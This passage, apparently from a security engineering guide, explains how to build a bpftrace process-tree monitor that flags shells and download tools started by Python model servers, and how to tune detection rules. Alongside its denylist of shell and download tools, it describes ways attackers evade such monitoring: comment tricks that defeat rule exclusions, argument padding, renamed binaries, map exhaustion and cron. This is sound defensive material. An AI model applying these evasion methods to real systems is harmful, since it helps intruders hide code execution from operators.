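3. Process 4207 calls execve and becomes a shell.
4. The clone call returns 4207 to process 4100, and the monitor adds that number to its watch list.

The monitor has missed the shell by the time it reaches step 4. Dileo reports that a tracer built this way loses some of a child's first operations more than 99% of the time. If the child quickly creates a child of its own, the tracer misses that second creation almost every time. Missing one process also makes the monitor miss its descendants. If 4207 isn't on the list when it creates 4208, the monitor never adds 4208 and doesn't report curl.

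With os.system, the bad order may occur every time. Current versions of the GNU C library create the shell with an option that suspends the calling thread until the child has called execve or exited, so the clone call always returns too late.

Dileo corrects this by recording the child after it is created but before it runs. The kernel creates processes and threads in one internal function, which calls `wake_up_new_task` to let the new process or thread start. The tracer attaches a kprobe, a probe on a chosen kernel function, to `wake_up_new_task`. The version below follows his bpftrace script with small changes.

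```
kprobe:wake_up_new_task
{
    $child = (struct task_struct *)arg0;
    @born[$child->pid] = nsecs;
}

tracepoint:syscalls:sys_enter_execve
/@born[pid]/
{
    $age_ms = (nsecs - @born[pid]) / 1000000;
    if ($age_ms <= 10) {
        printf("%s => ", comm);
        join(args.argv);
    }
    delete(@born[pid]);
}
```

The first block runs just before the child starts and stores the current time in the map `@born` under the child's pid. The second runs when a process calls execve. If the process is in the map and is at most 10 milliseconds old, the script prints its current comm and the new program's arguments, then deletes the entry. The child can't run until the first block has finished, so its entry is always in the map when it calls execve.

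The script demonstrates the fix but needs changes before it can monitor a model server. It reports only processes that call execve within 10 milliseconds of their creation, so it misses a child that takes longer on a busy machine. A model monitor should instead check whether the parent is on the watch list and, if so, add the child. The script also reports execve calls that fail, because it uses the entry hook. Moving the second block to sched_process_exec fixes that. Entries for children that never call execve stay in the map, so the monitor should remove them when the process exits.

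The tracepoint sched_process_fork is a simpler place for the first block. The kernel reaches it a few lines before `wake_up_new_task`. Dileo prefers the kprobe because it gives access to a complete description of the child, but accepts the tracepoint for a tracer that needs only the pid. *Adventures in Hooking Process and Thread Spawn Events* (2021) describes a programmer's attempts to avoid the tracepoint. A probe on the return from clone gave pids that were valid only inside a container, and a probe on another internal function always gave a pid of zero, for reasons the programmer never found, but the tracepoint worked. Kernel developers also try to keep a tracepoint's data stable between versions, which they don't promise for internal functions, so sched_process_fork is the better choice for the watch list.

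Hooking the shared internal function also covers all the system calls that create processes. Before version 0.5.4, Tracee added a child to its list after a fork, vfork or clone call but not after a call to clone3, a newer variant, so it didn't follow children created that way. Switching to sched_process_fork fixed this.

The monitor should also store the parent's pid at this moment instead of looking it up later. If a parent exits before its child calls execve, the kernel gives the child a new parent, and a lookup at execve returns that one. The monitor would then lose the link to the model, even though it had recorded the program start correctly. Because the watch list is in the kernel, it doesn't depend on the order in which records reach user space.

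### Which kernel the monitor covers

An eBPF program reports events only from the kernel that runs it. A monitor on a server can therefore report program starts by a model process only if that server's kernel handles the process's execve calls.

Ordinary containers, such as those Docker starts on a Linux server, meet this condition because they share the host's kernel, and they need no monitoring software of their own.

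Each container usually has its own process-number namespace, so the same process has one pid inside the container and another on the host. Process 4100 on the host might be number 1 in its container, and the shell, 4207 on the host, might be number 7. Clone returns 7 to its caller, because that is the shell's number inside the container. A host monitor that put 7 on its watch list would follow an unrelated process, or none. Dileo found that Tracee's process following didn't work on containers by default for this reason.

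The sched_process_fork tracepoint and the helper that the earlier example used to get the current PID give the host's PID. An engineer investigating from inside the container will see only PID 7, so an alert should include both PIDs and the container's name. Tracee began recording both PIDs when it changed hooks. While the process is running, the NSpid line in /proc/4207/status also shows them.

A virtual machine has its own kernel. When a process inside it calls execve, the guest kernel handles the call, so the host's kernel has no matching program start to report, and a monitor on the host would show only the process that runs the virtual machine. To cover a model running in the guest, the operator has to install the monitor there. This also applies to Kata Containers, which look like ordinary containers to the user but each run in a small virtual machine, and to Docker Desktop on a Mac,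 which runs all containers inside a Linux virtual machine.

gVisor, a sandbox that Google developed for untrusted containers, works differently again. It puts a kernel written as an ordinary user-space program between the container and the host. This program receives the container's system calls and carries out most of them itself, with a limited set of calls to the host's kernel. When Python starts a shell inside the sandbox, gVisor loads the shell, and the host's kernel never handles an execve for /bin/sh. A host monitor may still report gVisor's own processes, so the server can appear to have coverage when program starts inside the sandbox are missing. gVisor has a separate facility for sending events to a monitor, and the operator has to connect it. An organisation that moves its riskiest models into gVisor for better isolation could otherwise lose its program-start alerts for exactly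 those models.

On a managed service such as AWS Fargate, the provider runs the machine and the customer supplies only a container. The customer has no administrator access to the underlying Linux kernel, so they can't load eBPF programs. A hosted model service that offers only a web interface gives even less access, and the customer depends on whatever process monitoring the provider offers.

When no other monitoring is possible, Python's audit hooks can still report calls to os.system and subprocess from inside the process. But malicious code from a model file runs in the same process and may be able to avoid or disable them. The customer can also load each new model first on a machine where they control the kernel and can run the full monitor. This can catch a file that starts a shell as soon as it loads, but not one that waits until it is in production.

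Operators can check whether the host's monitor covers a workload. If `uname -r` prints different kernel versions inside the workload and on the host, the monitor doesn't cover it. Matching versions don't prove that it does, since a virtual machine can run the same version as its host. A better test is to start a harmless program, such as `/bin/true`, from Python inside the workload and confirm that the alert arrives with the right container and parent process. Operators should repeat the test whenever the workload moves to another machine or container runtime.

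## Building the monitor in bpftrace

A bpftrace script consists mainly of probes. Each probe names an event, such as a tracepoint, and contains a block of statements to run when the event occurs. A condition between slashes restricts when the block runs. Names that begin with `@` are BPF maps, and those with `$` are variables that last for one run of the block. `args` holds the fields of the event, and built-in names such as `pid` and `comm` describe the process that caused it.

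We build the monitor below in four stages and apply each one to the earlier test case, in which Python process 4100 starts sh (4207) and sh starts curl (4208). The full command is `curl -s http://127.0.0.1:8000/; echo done`, and the shell runs `echo` itself.

### Stage 1: every program start on the machine

bpftrace comes with a script for listing program starts, which Gregg (2017), in *execsnoop.bt*, wrote as a short version of the older BCC tool. The version below does the same job but labels the process numbers instead of printing column headings.

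```
tracepoint:syscalls:sys_enter_exec*
{
    $parent = ((struct task_struct *)curtask)->real_parent;
    printf("%s pid=%d ppid=%d ",
        strftime("%H:%M:%S", nsecs), pid, $parent->pid);
    join(args.argv);
}
```

The asterisk makes the probe cover both execve and execveat. `curtask` is the address of the kernel's `task_struct` for the current process, from which the script finds the parent. `join` prints the arguments with spaces between them. The test case should produce two lines:

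```
14:02:11 pid=4207 ppid=4100 sh -c curl -s http://127.0.0.1:8000/; echo done
14:02:11 pid=4208 ppid=4207 curl -s http://127.0.0.1:8000/
```

This is enough to see the attack if someone is watching the output and few other programs are starting on the machine. The script doesn't filter anything, so every cron job and login on the host appears in the same list.

It also prints at most 16 arguments, according to Gregg's manual page. The limit rarely affects shells, because the whole command after `-c` counts as one argument. But if malicious code starts `curl` directly and puts fifteen harmless options before the web address, the address is the seventeenth argument, counting `curl` itself, and doesn't appear.

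The script prints argv but not the path of the program file, and the caller can put anything in argv. For example, Python code can start `/usr/bin/curl` with `python3` as `argv[0]`, and the output would then show `python3` instead of `curl`.

The script doesn't check the return value, so it also prints failed attempts to start a program. In Gregg's sample output, recorded while someone opened a manual page, 8 of the 17 lines are failed attempts from searching PATH.

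### Stage 2: a filter on the process name

The obvious way to shorten the list is to keep only the calls that come from Python:

```
tracepoint:syscalls:sys_enter_exec*
/comm == "python3"/
{
    printf("%-6d %-16s ", pid, comm);
    join(args.argv);
}
```

For the test case, this prints one line:

```
4207   python3          sh -c curl -s http://127.0.0.1:8000/; echo done
```

The filter catches the shell because process 4207 is still a copy of Python when it calls execve and has inherited Python's comm. ringzeropirate's *Your First eBPF Hook*, a tutorial on a personal blog, describes comm at this point as the parent's name. The two names are usually the same, but the value belongs to the child. The filter discards curl because process 4208 is a copy of the shell, so its comm is `sh`.

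Adding `sh` to the filter would catch curl, along with every program that any shell on the machine starts.

The filter can also miss the first shell, because a Python process isn't always called `python3`. If someone starts the server with `python` or `python3.12`, the process has a different comm. Many Python packages also install a command that is a short script whose first line names the interpreter. If an operator starts the model server vLLM through such a command, the kernel sets comm to the script's name, `vllm`.

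Matching on `python3` can also miss a shell that a worker thread starts, because each thread has its own comm and a child process inherits the comm of the thread that created it. Since version 3.14, Python has passed the names of its threads to the operating system, where the kernel keeps only the first 15 characters. A server that loads models in a ThreadPoolExecutor, Python's standard pool of worker threads, therefore has threads named `ThreadPoolExecu`.

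The 15-character limit also affects filters for longer names. In one of Dileo's tests, a program called `userns-clone-fork` appears as `userns-clone-fo`, so a filter for the full name would never match it.

bpftrace's *0.25 Release Notes* introduce `pcomm`, which returns the name of the process instead of the thread. It doesn't help here. By the time execve runs, the child is a separate process, and the name it inherited from the worker thread has become its process name.

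Malicious code can also rename itself. Any thread can change its comm by writing a new name to /proc/thread-self/comm, and a model file can make Python do this just before it starts a shell. A name filter is useful for a first look at a machine, but a monitor needs to filter on something the process can't change.

### Stage 3: following the process tree

A process can't change which process created it, so the third version uses that relationship to build a watch list in a map called `@root`. When a program starts from a file whose name begins with "python", the script adds the process and any child processes it creates to the map.

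```
tracepoint:sched:sched_process_exec
{
    $task = (struct task_struct *)curtask;
    $file = str($task->mm->exe_file->f_path.dentry->d_name.name);

    if (@root[tid]) {
        printf("root=%d parent=%d pid=%d %s\n",
            @root[tid], @parent[tid], pid, str(args.filename));
    } else if (strncmp($file, "python", 6) == 0) {
        @root[tid] = pid;
        @parent[tid] = (uint32)$task->real_parent->tgid;
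    }
}

tracepoint:sched:sched_process_fork
/@root[tid]/
{
    $child = (uint32)args.child_pid;
    @root[$child] = @root[tid];
    @parent[$child] = pid;
}

tracepoint:sched:sched_process_exit
/@root[tid]/
{
    delete(@root, tid);
    delete(@parent, tid);
}
```

The long expression in the first probe follows pointers from `task_struct` to the file that the process is now running, and reads that file's own name. For the vLLM command, the result is something like `python3.12`, even though comm is `vllm`. Thread names don't affect that result.

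The test case now goes as follows:

1. Python starts as process 4100, and the first probe stores `@root[4100] = 4100`.
2. Process 4100 creates 4207. The second probe finds 4100 in the map and stores `@root[4207] = 4100` before the child can run.
3. Process 4207 becomes sh. The first probe finds it in the map and prints a record.
4. The shell creates 4208, which the second probe adds with the same root.
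5. Process 4208 becomes curl, and the first probe prints another record.
6. As each process exits, the third probe removes it.

```
root=4100 parent=4100 pid=4207 /bin/sh
root=4100 parent=4207 pid=4208 /usr/bin/curl
```

Both records contain the number of the Python process, so an operator can tell at once which model server was responsible.

**Threads and processes.** The kernel gives every thread a number, which it calls a pid. The process ID that users see is the kernel's "thread group ID", or tgid, according to a comment in Gregg and Xing's version of execsnoop. In bpftrace, `tid` is the thread's number and `pid` is the process's. They are the same only for a process's main thread.

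If thread 4111 of process 4100 calls `os.system`, the fork event's `parent_pid` field contains the thread's ID, 4111. `execsnoop.bt` also reports 4111 as the parent because it reads `real_parent->pid`, but an ordinary process list has no process 4111. The script avoids this problem by reading `pid` inside the probe. Kernel code that Dileo quotes passes the current task to this tracepoint as the parent, so `pid` is 4100, the parent process's ID.

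The fork tracepoint also fires for new threads, and the exit tracepoint fires each time one ends, so `@root` has an entry for every thread. If the script kept one entry per process and deleted it by `pid`, the first worker thread to finish would remove the server from the watch list. The monitor would keep running but report nothing more from that server.

The monitor deletes entries because Linux reuses process IDs, and an old entry for 4207 would eventually apply to an unrelated process. Deleting a parent's entry leaves its children's entries in place, so the monitor still tracks a background program after the shell that started it exits.

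As written, the script follows every Python process that starts on the host, including system tools. If the model server runs under its own account, the operator can limit the script to that account's Python processes by adding a `uid` test to the `strncmp` condition.

The script has no record of a server that was already running when the monitor started. Using bpftrace's `-p 4100` option wouldn't solve this because, according to the manual, it discards tracepoint events from every other process. Those events would include both program starts in the test case.

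A better solution uses the server's cgroup, the kernel's grouping of processes for resource control. Each container or system service normally has one. The following extra probe adds the children of any process in the chosen group:

```
tracepoint:sched:sched_process_fork
/!@root[tid] &&
 cgroup == cgroupid("/sys/fs/cgroup/system.slice/model.service")/
{
    $child = (uint32)args.child_pid;
    @root[$child] = pid;
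    @parent[$child] = pid;
}
```

bpftrace's *stdlib.md*, the function reference for version 0.24.1, lists two restrictions. `cgroup` works only with version 2 of the cgroup system, and bpftrace looks up the path once, when it compiles the script. A restarted container may get a new cgroup with a new number, so the operator has to restart the monitor as well. The probe also misses a running server that replaces itself with a shell without creating a child. Restarting the server under the monitor covers both cases.

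Tracking by cgroup and tracking by ancestry can select different processes. When an administrator opens a shell with `docker exec`, Docker puts it in the container's cgroup, but the shell doesn't descend from the model server. With the Python seed, the monitor ignores that shell, while the cgroup probe adds whatever the shell starts. On a production server, an operator may well want to see programs started by both the model server and the shell.

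Whatever seed is chosen, following the process tree misses programs that malicious code starts through an unrelated service. For instance, the code can add a job to the account's crontab. The program then descends from cron, so the monitor doesn't report it. A container without cron or access to the Docker control socket gives an attacker fewer ways to do this.

### Stage 4: the full script

The last version adds the details an alert needs and marks shells and download tools for immediate attention. It still records every other program start in the tree.

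```
config = {
    max_strlen = 512;
    max_map_keys = 65536;
}

tracepoint:sched:sched_process_exec
{
    $task = (struct task_struct *)curtask;
    $file = str($task->mm->exe_file->f_path.dentry->d_name.name);
    $old = (uint32)args.old_pid;

    if (!@root[$old]) {
        if (strncmp($file, "python", 6) == 0) {
            @root[tid] = pid;
            @parent[tid] = (uint32)$task->real_parent->tgid;
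        }
        return;
    }

    if ($old != tid) {        /* a worker thread made the call */
        @root[tid] = @root[$old];
        @parent[tid] = @parent[$old];
        delete(@root, $old);
        delete(@parent, $old);
    }

    $known = $file == "sh" || $file == "dash" || $file == "bash" ||
             $file == "busybox" || $file == "curl" || $file == "wget";
    $start = $task->mm->arg_start;
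    $len = $task->mm->arg_end - $start;

    printf("%s %s root=%d parent=%d pid=%d uid=%d cgroup=%s path=%s file=%s argv(%d)=%r\n",
        strftime("%H:%M:%S", nsecs), $known ? "ALERT" : "START",
        @root[tid], @parent[tid], pid, uid, cgroup_path(cgroup),
        str(args.filename), $file,
        $len, buf(uptr((uint8 *)$start), $len));
}

tracepoint:sched:sched_process_fork
/@root[tid]/
{
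    $child = (uint32)args.child_pid;
    @root[$child] = @root[tid];
    @parent[$child] = pid;
}

tracepoint:sched:sched_process_exit
/@root[tid]/
{
    delete(@root, tid);
    delete(@parent, tid);
}
```

For the test case, the two records should look like this, with line breaks added:

```
14:02:11 ALERT root=4100 parent=4100 pid=4207 uid=1001
  cgroup=unified:/system.slice/model.service path=/bin/sh file=dash
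  argv(48)=sh\x00-c\x00curl -s http://127.0.0.1:8000/; echo done\x00
14:02:11 ALERT root=4100 parent=4207 pid=4208 uid=1001
  cgroup=unified:/system.slice/model.service path=/usr/bin/curl file=curl
  argv(31)=curl\x00-s\x00http://127.0.0.1:8000/\x00
```

The script needs no separate check for success, because `sched_process_exec` fires only for successful calls.

`$old` handles the uncommon case where a worker thread, say 4111, calls execve and takes over the main thread's number, 4100. By then the exit probe has deleted the entry for 4100, so looking up `tid` would find nothing, and the script would miss a shell that had replaced the whole server. The script therefore looks up 4111, which is still available in `old_pid`, and then moves that entry to 4100.

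The arguments come from the new program's memory, where the kernel stores them one after another, each followed by a zero byte. `str` would stop at the first zero byte and print only `sh`, so the script uses `buf`, which copies the whole block and prints each zero byte as `\x00`. The number in brackets is the full length in bytes.

**Matching the file rather than the requested path.** The records include both `path` and `file` because the caller controls `path`, which is the text it passed to execve. A rule that checked `path` for exactly `/usr/bin/curl` would miss `/usr/bin//curl`, although the kernel opens the same file for both. It would also miss a symbolic link with another name. `file` is the name of the file the kernel opened, so it is the same in all these cases. It also identifies the shell that runs a script. If Python runs `/tmp/setup`, whose first line names `/bin/sh`, `path`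 is `/tmp/setup` and `file` is `dash`.

The full resolved path would be better still, since it would distinguish /usr/bin/curl from a file called curl in /tmp. bpftrace's `path` function returns this, but according to *stdlib.md* it is restricted to a list of kernel functions that the kernel's developers have approved, so the tracepoint used here can't call it.

Small container images often use BusyBox, which combines a shell, wget and many other tools in one executable. In such a container `file` is always `busybox`, so the operator has to read `path` or argv to see which tool ran.

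Neither field identifies a program that has been copied under a new name. Malicious Python code can copy /usr/bin/curl to /tmp/helper without starting another program, then run the copy. The script records this as `START` with `file=helper`, because it prints every program start in the tree and uses the list of names only to set the label. A monitor that printed only matches would miss it. An unfamiliar program in a temporary directory may deserve more attention than curl does, so operators should also read the `START` records once they have exceptions for the programs their server normally runs.

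**String limits.** bpftrace has to reserve space for strings in advance. Version 0.20.2 allows 64 bytes by default, which is too short for many shell commands, so the script raises the limit to 512. An attacker can still put 600 spaces before the command in the test case. The shell ignores them, but they fill the room available for the arguments, and curl's address doesn't appear. The record would show `argv(648)`, so the reader can see that most of the command is missing. When `str` cuts off a long path, bpftrace marks the cut with two dots by default.

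Maps also have a size limit, which was 4,096 keys by default in version 0.20.2. Because the script uses one key per thread, a malicious model file could create thousands of threads to fill the map, then start a shell that the script has no room to add. Raising the limit to 65,536 makes this harder. Limiting the number of threads in the server's cgroup to well below the size of the map would stop a single server from filling it.

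### Testing

The operator can first test the script with `--dry-run`, which makes bpftrace compile, load and attach the script and then exit. This should reveal most incompatibilities with the installed version. If a field is missing, `bpftrace -lv 'tracepoint:sched:sched_process_exec'` lists the fields the kernel provides.

The test doesn't need a malicious file, or even a pickle. In one terminal, `python3 -m http.server 8000 --bind 127.0.0.1` starts a small local web server. With the monitor running in a second terminal, this command in a third produces the test case:

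```
python3 -c 'import os; os.system("curl -s http://127.0.0.1:8000/; echo done")'
```

Further triggers check the parts of the script that are easiest to get wrong:

| Action inside Python | Expected result |
|---|---|
| Call os.system from a worker thread | The same two records, with the Python process as root |
| Replace Python with curl from a worker thread, using os.execv | One `ALERT`, with the Python process's own number as both pid and parent |
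| Run curl through the subprocess module without giving its directory | One `ALERT`, although execsnoop.bt may print several lines |
| Copy curl to /tmp/helper and run it | One `START` with `file=helper` |
| Call os.fork and start nothing | No record |

When the operator stops the monitor with Ctrl-C, bpftrace prints the contents of both maps. Any entry for a thread that no longer exists points to a mistake in the cleanup. The `-k` option, which makes bpftrace log failed memory reads with their error codes, can help explain an unexpectedly blank field.

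bpftrace can also start the test program itself with `-c`. The program then runs with bpftrace's privileges, usually as root, so this option is unsuitable for loading an untrusted model.

### Privileges and running as a service

Older versions of bpftrace must run as root. Version 0.25 instead checks for four Linux capabilities, each of which grants part of root's power: CAP_BPF, CAP_PERFMON, CAP_DAC_READ_SEARCH and CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE. CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE lets a process ignore file permissions, even when writing, so the monitor's account needs nearly as much protection as root, and the model server must not be able to change the script.

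The monitor should run on the host. If it runs inside a container with its own process numbers, `pid` and `tid` may not match the host numbers in the tracepoint's fields.

A systemd service can start the monitor at boot and restart it after a crash:

```
[Service]
ExecStart=/usr/bin/bpftrace -f json /etc/model-monitor/follow.bt
Restart=always

[Install]
WantedBy=multi-user.target
```

bpftrace's `-f json` option makes each line of output a valid JSON object. ringzeropirate's tutorial instead builds JSON by hand with printf, which breaks if a filename contains a quotation mark. In plain-text output, an attacker could use a filename with a line break to add a convincing false record. The built-in option should escape such characters. The tutorial also discards bpftrace's error messages, but a service should keep them because they may be the only sign of a problem.

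After the service starts, bpftrace has to compile the script and attach the probes before monitoring begins. A Python server that starts in the meantime won't be in the map. The safest approach is to run the harmless trigger, wait for its alert and only then start the model server.

Restarting the monitor automatically leaves a similar gap. The maps disappear when bpftrace exits, so the new monitor doesn't track a server that is already running. With the cgroup probe from Stage 3, the monitor still covers new child processes of that server. Without the probe, the operator has to restart the server.

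### Differences between versions

The version of bpftrace depends heavily on the Linux distribution. In September 2026, Debian's *bpftrace* page listed 0.17.0 in oldstable, 0.23.2 in stable, 0.26.1 in testing and 0.27.0 in unstable. Ubuntu's version was 0.25.0.

The script uses the current form `delete(@root, tid)`. Versions up to 0.21 expect `delete(@root[tid])`, which later versions still accept but have deprecated. Older scripts also write `args->argv` where current ones write `args.argv`. Changing the notation isn't enough to make this script run on an old version such as 0.20.2, which kept strings on the 512-byte eBPF stack. A single string at the script's limit would fill that stack.

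Version 0.25 changed how bpftrace converts between integer types. The script converts the tracepoint's process numbers to `uint32` so that they match the type of `tid` in every comparison. An operator should repeat the dry run and the tests after each bpftrace or kernel upgrade.

### When to write a compiled program

bpftrace is well suited to developing a detection rule and to watching a few servers. DevConf.CZ's *bpftrace* (2026), the summary of a conference talk, acknowledges that the tool has struggled with complex applications that have to run for long periods. Its developers are working on this. Scannell and Rome (2025) describe plans for reusable code, a standard library and a way to combine scripts with eBPF code written in C.

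For now, a compiled program based on libbpf has several advantages over a bpftrace script for a permanent monitor. It can keep its maps in the kernel when the user-space part restarts, which closes the gap described above. It can count lost records itself and give program starts their own buffer. It also doesn't need bpftrace and its compiler on every server, and it can send structured fields instead of one formatted line.

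BCC's *execsnoop.c*, a libbpf version of execsnoop with options for failed calls, users, cgroups and the number of arguments, is a reasonable starting point. A developer would still have to add the process tree, but the three probes above translate almost line by line into C.

Replacing the bpftrace script is worthwhile when the monitor must restart without losing track of a server, or when the operator has too many machines to check each bpftrace version by hand. Until then, the script is preferable because it is easier to read and correct. The operator can test the replacement with the same triggers.

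## Telling unexpected child processes from normal ones

The bpftrace script records every program that a Python server or one of its descendants starts. On a healthy machine all of those records are harmless, but an operator can't quickly tell that without knowing what the server normally runs. Machine-learning code also starts more programs than one might expect from software that mostly does arithmetic, and some of them look alarming.

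### Programs that harmless code starts

| Program | What starts it | When |
|---|---|---|
| g++, cc1plus, as, ld | PyTorch, to build native code | First run of a model |
| ldconfig, sometimes gcc, objdump or ld | Python's `find_library` function | Import of a package that needs a C library |
| uname, file | Python's `platform` module | Usually start-up |
| git, nvidia-smi | Experiment loggers | Start of a run, or every few seconds |
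| ffmpeg | Speech and video software | Each request |
| pip, conda, and shells they start | Package installation | Builds and notebooks |
| python3 | Python's `multiprocessing` module | When workers start |

The compiler processes come from `torch.compile`, a PyTorch feature that translates a model into faster native code when the model first runs. On a CPU, it generates C++ and compiles it. According to PyTorch's *cpp builder*, the source file for this step, PyTorch tests candidate compilers by running each with `--version`, then starts the chosen one without a shell. The compiler g++ starts several other programs to translate, assemble and link the code, so compiling one small piece of a model can add five or more records.

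The same source file has an option, set through the environment variable `TORCH_INDUCTOR_INSTALL_GXX`, that lets PyTorch start conda, download a compiler and run it. In a process log, this looks just like the attack this monitor is meant to detect, where a model server downloads an executable and runs it. The option is off by default and should stay off on production servers.

Performance settings can also change the list of expected child processes. On a GPU, `torch.compile` produces the GPU code and a separate wrapper that launches it. PyTorch Conference Europe's *Accelerating PyTorch Models With torch.compile's Cpp Wrapper Mode* (2026) describes a mode that replaces the Python wrapper with a compiled C one. If an engineer turns this mode on to save time per request, the server may also start a compiler as a child process.

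Python's standard library sometimes starts programs where few developers would expect it to. On Linux, `find_library` tries to run `/sbin/ldconfig`, gcc, objdump and ld to locate a C library, according to Python's *ctypes* documentation. The audio package soundfile depends on this function, and Rodriguez Garcia ran into the behavior on a small embedded device where none of these tools made sense. A speech model that never compiles anything may therefore still start gcc. The documentation suggests hardcoding the library's name instead, which would also remove these program starts from the monitoring records.

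On some Ubuntu releases, `/sbin/ldconfig` is a short shell script that runs the real program. The bpftrace script would report it with `path=/sbin/ldconfig` and `file=dash`, and label it `ALERT`.

The `platform` module can cause a similar false alarm, depending on the version of Python. According to a report on Python's bug tracker, almost any call to the module ran `sh -c uname -p`. After a later change, *bpo-35967 resolve platform.processor late (GH-12239)*, the module runs uname directly, and only when a program looks up the processor type. In LLVM's copy of the newer module, `platform.platform()` still looks it up on Linux, while `platform.system()` doesn't. The same line of a model server's code can therefore start a shell on an old image but not on a new one.

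Upgrading Python can also add records. Python's *multiprocessing* documentation describes three ways to create worker processes. With `fork`, workers are copies of the parent and cause no program starts. With `spawn`, each worker is a fresh Python interpreter. With `forkserver`, Python starts one helper process, which then copies itself for each worker. Both `spawn` and `forkserver` also start a process that tracks shared resources. A job with eight workers therefore causes no program starts under `fork`, two under `forkserver` and nine under `spawn`. Python 3.14 changed the default on Linux from `fork` to `forkserver`, so a baseline from 3.13 will be wrong after the upgrade even if the application hasn't changed.

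These extra interpreters are fairly safe to permit. Malicious code in a Python process can already do anything Python can do, so it gains little by starting another copy. If that copy started a shell, the monitor would still report it.

Experiment loggers record how a training run went. *Settings*, the reference for the Weights & Biases (W&B) logger, lists options for capturing the state of the git repository and for sampling system metrics, which happens every 15 seconds by default. It also mentions an internal service called wandb-core that the logger waits for at start-up. A logger can collect this information through libraries or by running git and nvidia-smi. One that ran nvidia-smi for every sample would start it 5,760 times a day, and a monitor that alerted on every start would produce too many alerts to be useful. W&B has settings to disable git capture and system metrics.

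Speech-recognition software such as Whisper runs ffmpeg to decode audio. On a server that transcribes uploads, each recording from an outsider causes Python to start ffmpeg, which then reads that recording. It's reasonable for Python to start ffmpeg this way, but not for ffmpeg to start another program, so the monitor needs to record which program started which.

### How predictable each workload is

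An inference server is the easiest case because it runs the same code for weeks and launches most of its child programs at start-up or on the first request. An operator can make it more predictable by moving compilation out of production. PyTorch can compile a model ahead of time into a shared library, so the compiler runs on a build machine and the server doesn't need one.

Training jobs start more programs, but mostly near the beginning, when the logger captures its metadata, the workers start and PyTorch compiles the model. After that, a job may run for days, starting programs only to collect metrics at intervals. Researchers edit training code between runs, so a list of expected programs from last week's job may be out of date, but a shell that starts on the third day of a run is still unusual.

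Build steps start hundreds of programs, including shells, compilers and download tools, so a program's name alone is little help in spotting an unexpected one. Repeated builds of the same project start roughly the same programs, so comparing one build with the last can work. Elastic suggests excluding the working directories of known build systems from its Python shell rule. That is a reasonable way to reduce noise, but an attacker would want to work in those directories because build machines often hold credentials for publishing software.

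Notebooks are hard to monitor because users can run any shell command by typing an exclamation mark before it, so a shell start there is not in itself unexpected. AI agents are even harder to monitor because they start shells as part of their normal operation.

The operator can use the cgroup or container image in each record to apply different rules to different workloads. A single rule for all four workloads would either produce too many notebook alerts or need exceptions so broad that it would miss attacks on the inference servers.

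### A fixed list of forbidden programs

The simplest rule reports any child process whose name is on a list. The bpftrace script lists six names, which catch both program starts in the test case. The rule needs no history, so it works immediately on a new machine.

A rule based on a list of programs, like a scanner's denylist, misses whatever the list leaves out, such as a renamed copy of curl, a Perl script that downloads a file, or git. A list of every program that can reach the network would include git and ffmpeg, which harmless workloads need. The list of shells can also be incomplete. Elastic's first-occurrence rule, discussed below, names eight shells but not BusyBox. This matters little on macOS, but anyone adapting the rule for containers would have to add BusyBox.

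A narrower pattern can justify a more urgent alert. Elastic's *Interactive Terminal Spawned via Python* (2020) detects the use of Python to turn a reverse shell into a full terminal, which attackers often do after opening the shell. Elastic rates this rule high severity, with a risk score of 73, and rates its more general rules on Python and shells medium, with a score of 47. An inference server has almost no reason to open an interactive terminal, so this behavior is a good candidate for a fixed rule. The rule does not detect a model file that runs one command and exits.

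### First occurrence on a host

The alternative to naming bad programs is to report what is new. Elastic's rule for the first time Python starts a shell on a host works in four steps:

1. On macOS, it selects program starts where the parent's name begins with "python", the child is one of the eight shells and the arguments include `-c`.
2. It drops any whose command line contains "pip", "conda", "brew" or "jupyter".
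3. For each remaining event, it takes two values, the host's ID and the path of the Python executable.
4. It raises an alert if that pair hasn't appeared in the previous seven days.

The rule runs every five minutes, so the shell may have finished long before anyone sees the alert.

The pair in step 3 doesn't include the command. Suppose a Python service runs `sh -c "df -h"` every night to check disk space. The first run triggers an alert, which someone investigates and finds harmless. As long as the nightly check continues, the pair will always have been seen within the past day, so the rule won't alert on it again on that host. If a malicious model makes the same Python executable run `sh -c "curl ..."` a month later, the rule will miss it.

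Rare but legitimate work can look unexpected. A monthly retraining job that starts a shell looks new every month, and a new server has no history. Elastic's *New terms rules*, the general documentation for this type of rule, warns that a short history window causes excessive false alarms. A preview edition suggests 30 to 90 days for truly rare events, although longer windows slow searches, and recommends starting with a long window and shortening it later.

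The exclusions in step 2 are expensive for what they achieve. They match text anywhere in the shell's command line, and "pip" is also the start of "pipeline", a common word in machine-learning code. The rule would therefore ignore a shell that runs `/opt/pipeline/convert.sh`. An attacker can use the same gap by adding a comment to the test command:

```
curl -s http://127.0.0.1:8000/; echo done # pip
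```

The shell ignores everything after the `#`, and the rule ignores the shell.

Excluding pip also makes the rule miss a type of attack it is supposed to detect, because a malicious package can do its damage while pip installs it. According to Elastic's investigation notes, the filter excludes shells started by post-install scripts.

The "jupyter" exclusion does little to filter out shell commands run from notebooks. If someone types `!ls` in a notebook, the resulting shell command contains `ls` but may not contain "jupyter".

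A Linux version could avoid much of this. Rules of this type accept up to three fields, so an operator could use the container image, the parent's executable and the child's executable. The rule could also cover the whole process tree instead of only shells that Python starts directly. With these changes, the nightly `df` check would no longer hide the attack, because a shell starting curl would be a new combination. Using the image instead of the host ID would also let a new server share the history of older ones. The operator could exclude build jobs by image, which code inside the container can't change by adding a word to a command.

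Even this version can only compare new behaviour with old, so if a malicious model is already running when the history begins, the rule treats the model's shell as familiar.

### Several suspicious starts within a short time

Shells are common on a workstation, but it is less common for several to run in quick succession with commands that identify the user, identify the system and list its files. Elastic's *Suspicious Python Shell Command Execution* (2026) looks for such bursts on Linux and macOS.

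The rule selects shells, this time including BusyBox, that Python starts with `-c` or a close variant. It groups them by parent process and clock minute. It then searches the text of each command to sort it into one of seven kinds: grep, find, curl, wget, reading environment variables, identifying the machine or user, and everything else. The rule raises an alert only when a group contains at least five different command lines of at least four kinds.

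| Shell commands from one Python process | Different command lines | Kinds | Alert |
|---|---|---|---|
| `whoami`, `uname`, `env`, `find /`, `curl` with an address, in separate shells within one minute | 5 | 4 | Yes |
| The same five commands, separated by semicolons in one shell | 1 | 1 | No |
| The same five, one every 15 seconds | At most 4 a minute | At most 4 | No |
| The test case | 1 | 1 | No |
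| Notebook set-up: `uname -a`, `ls data`, `find data`, `wget` with an address, `pip install` | 5 | 4 | Yes |

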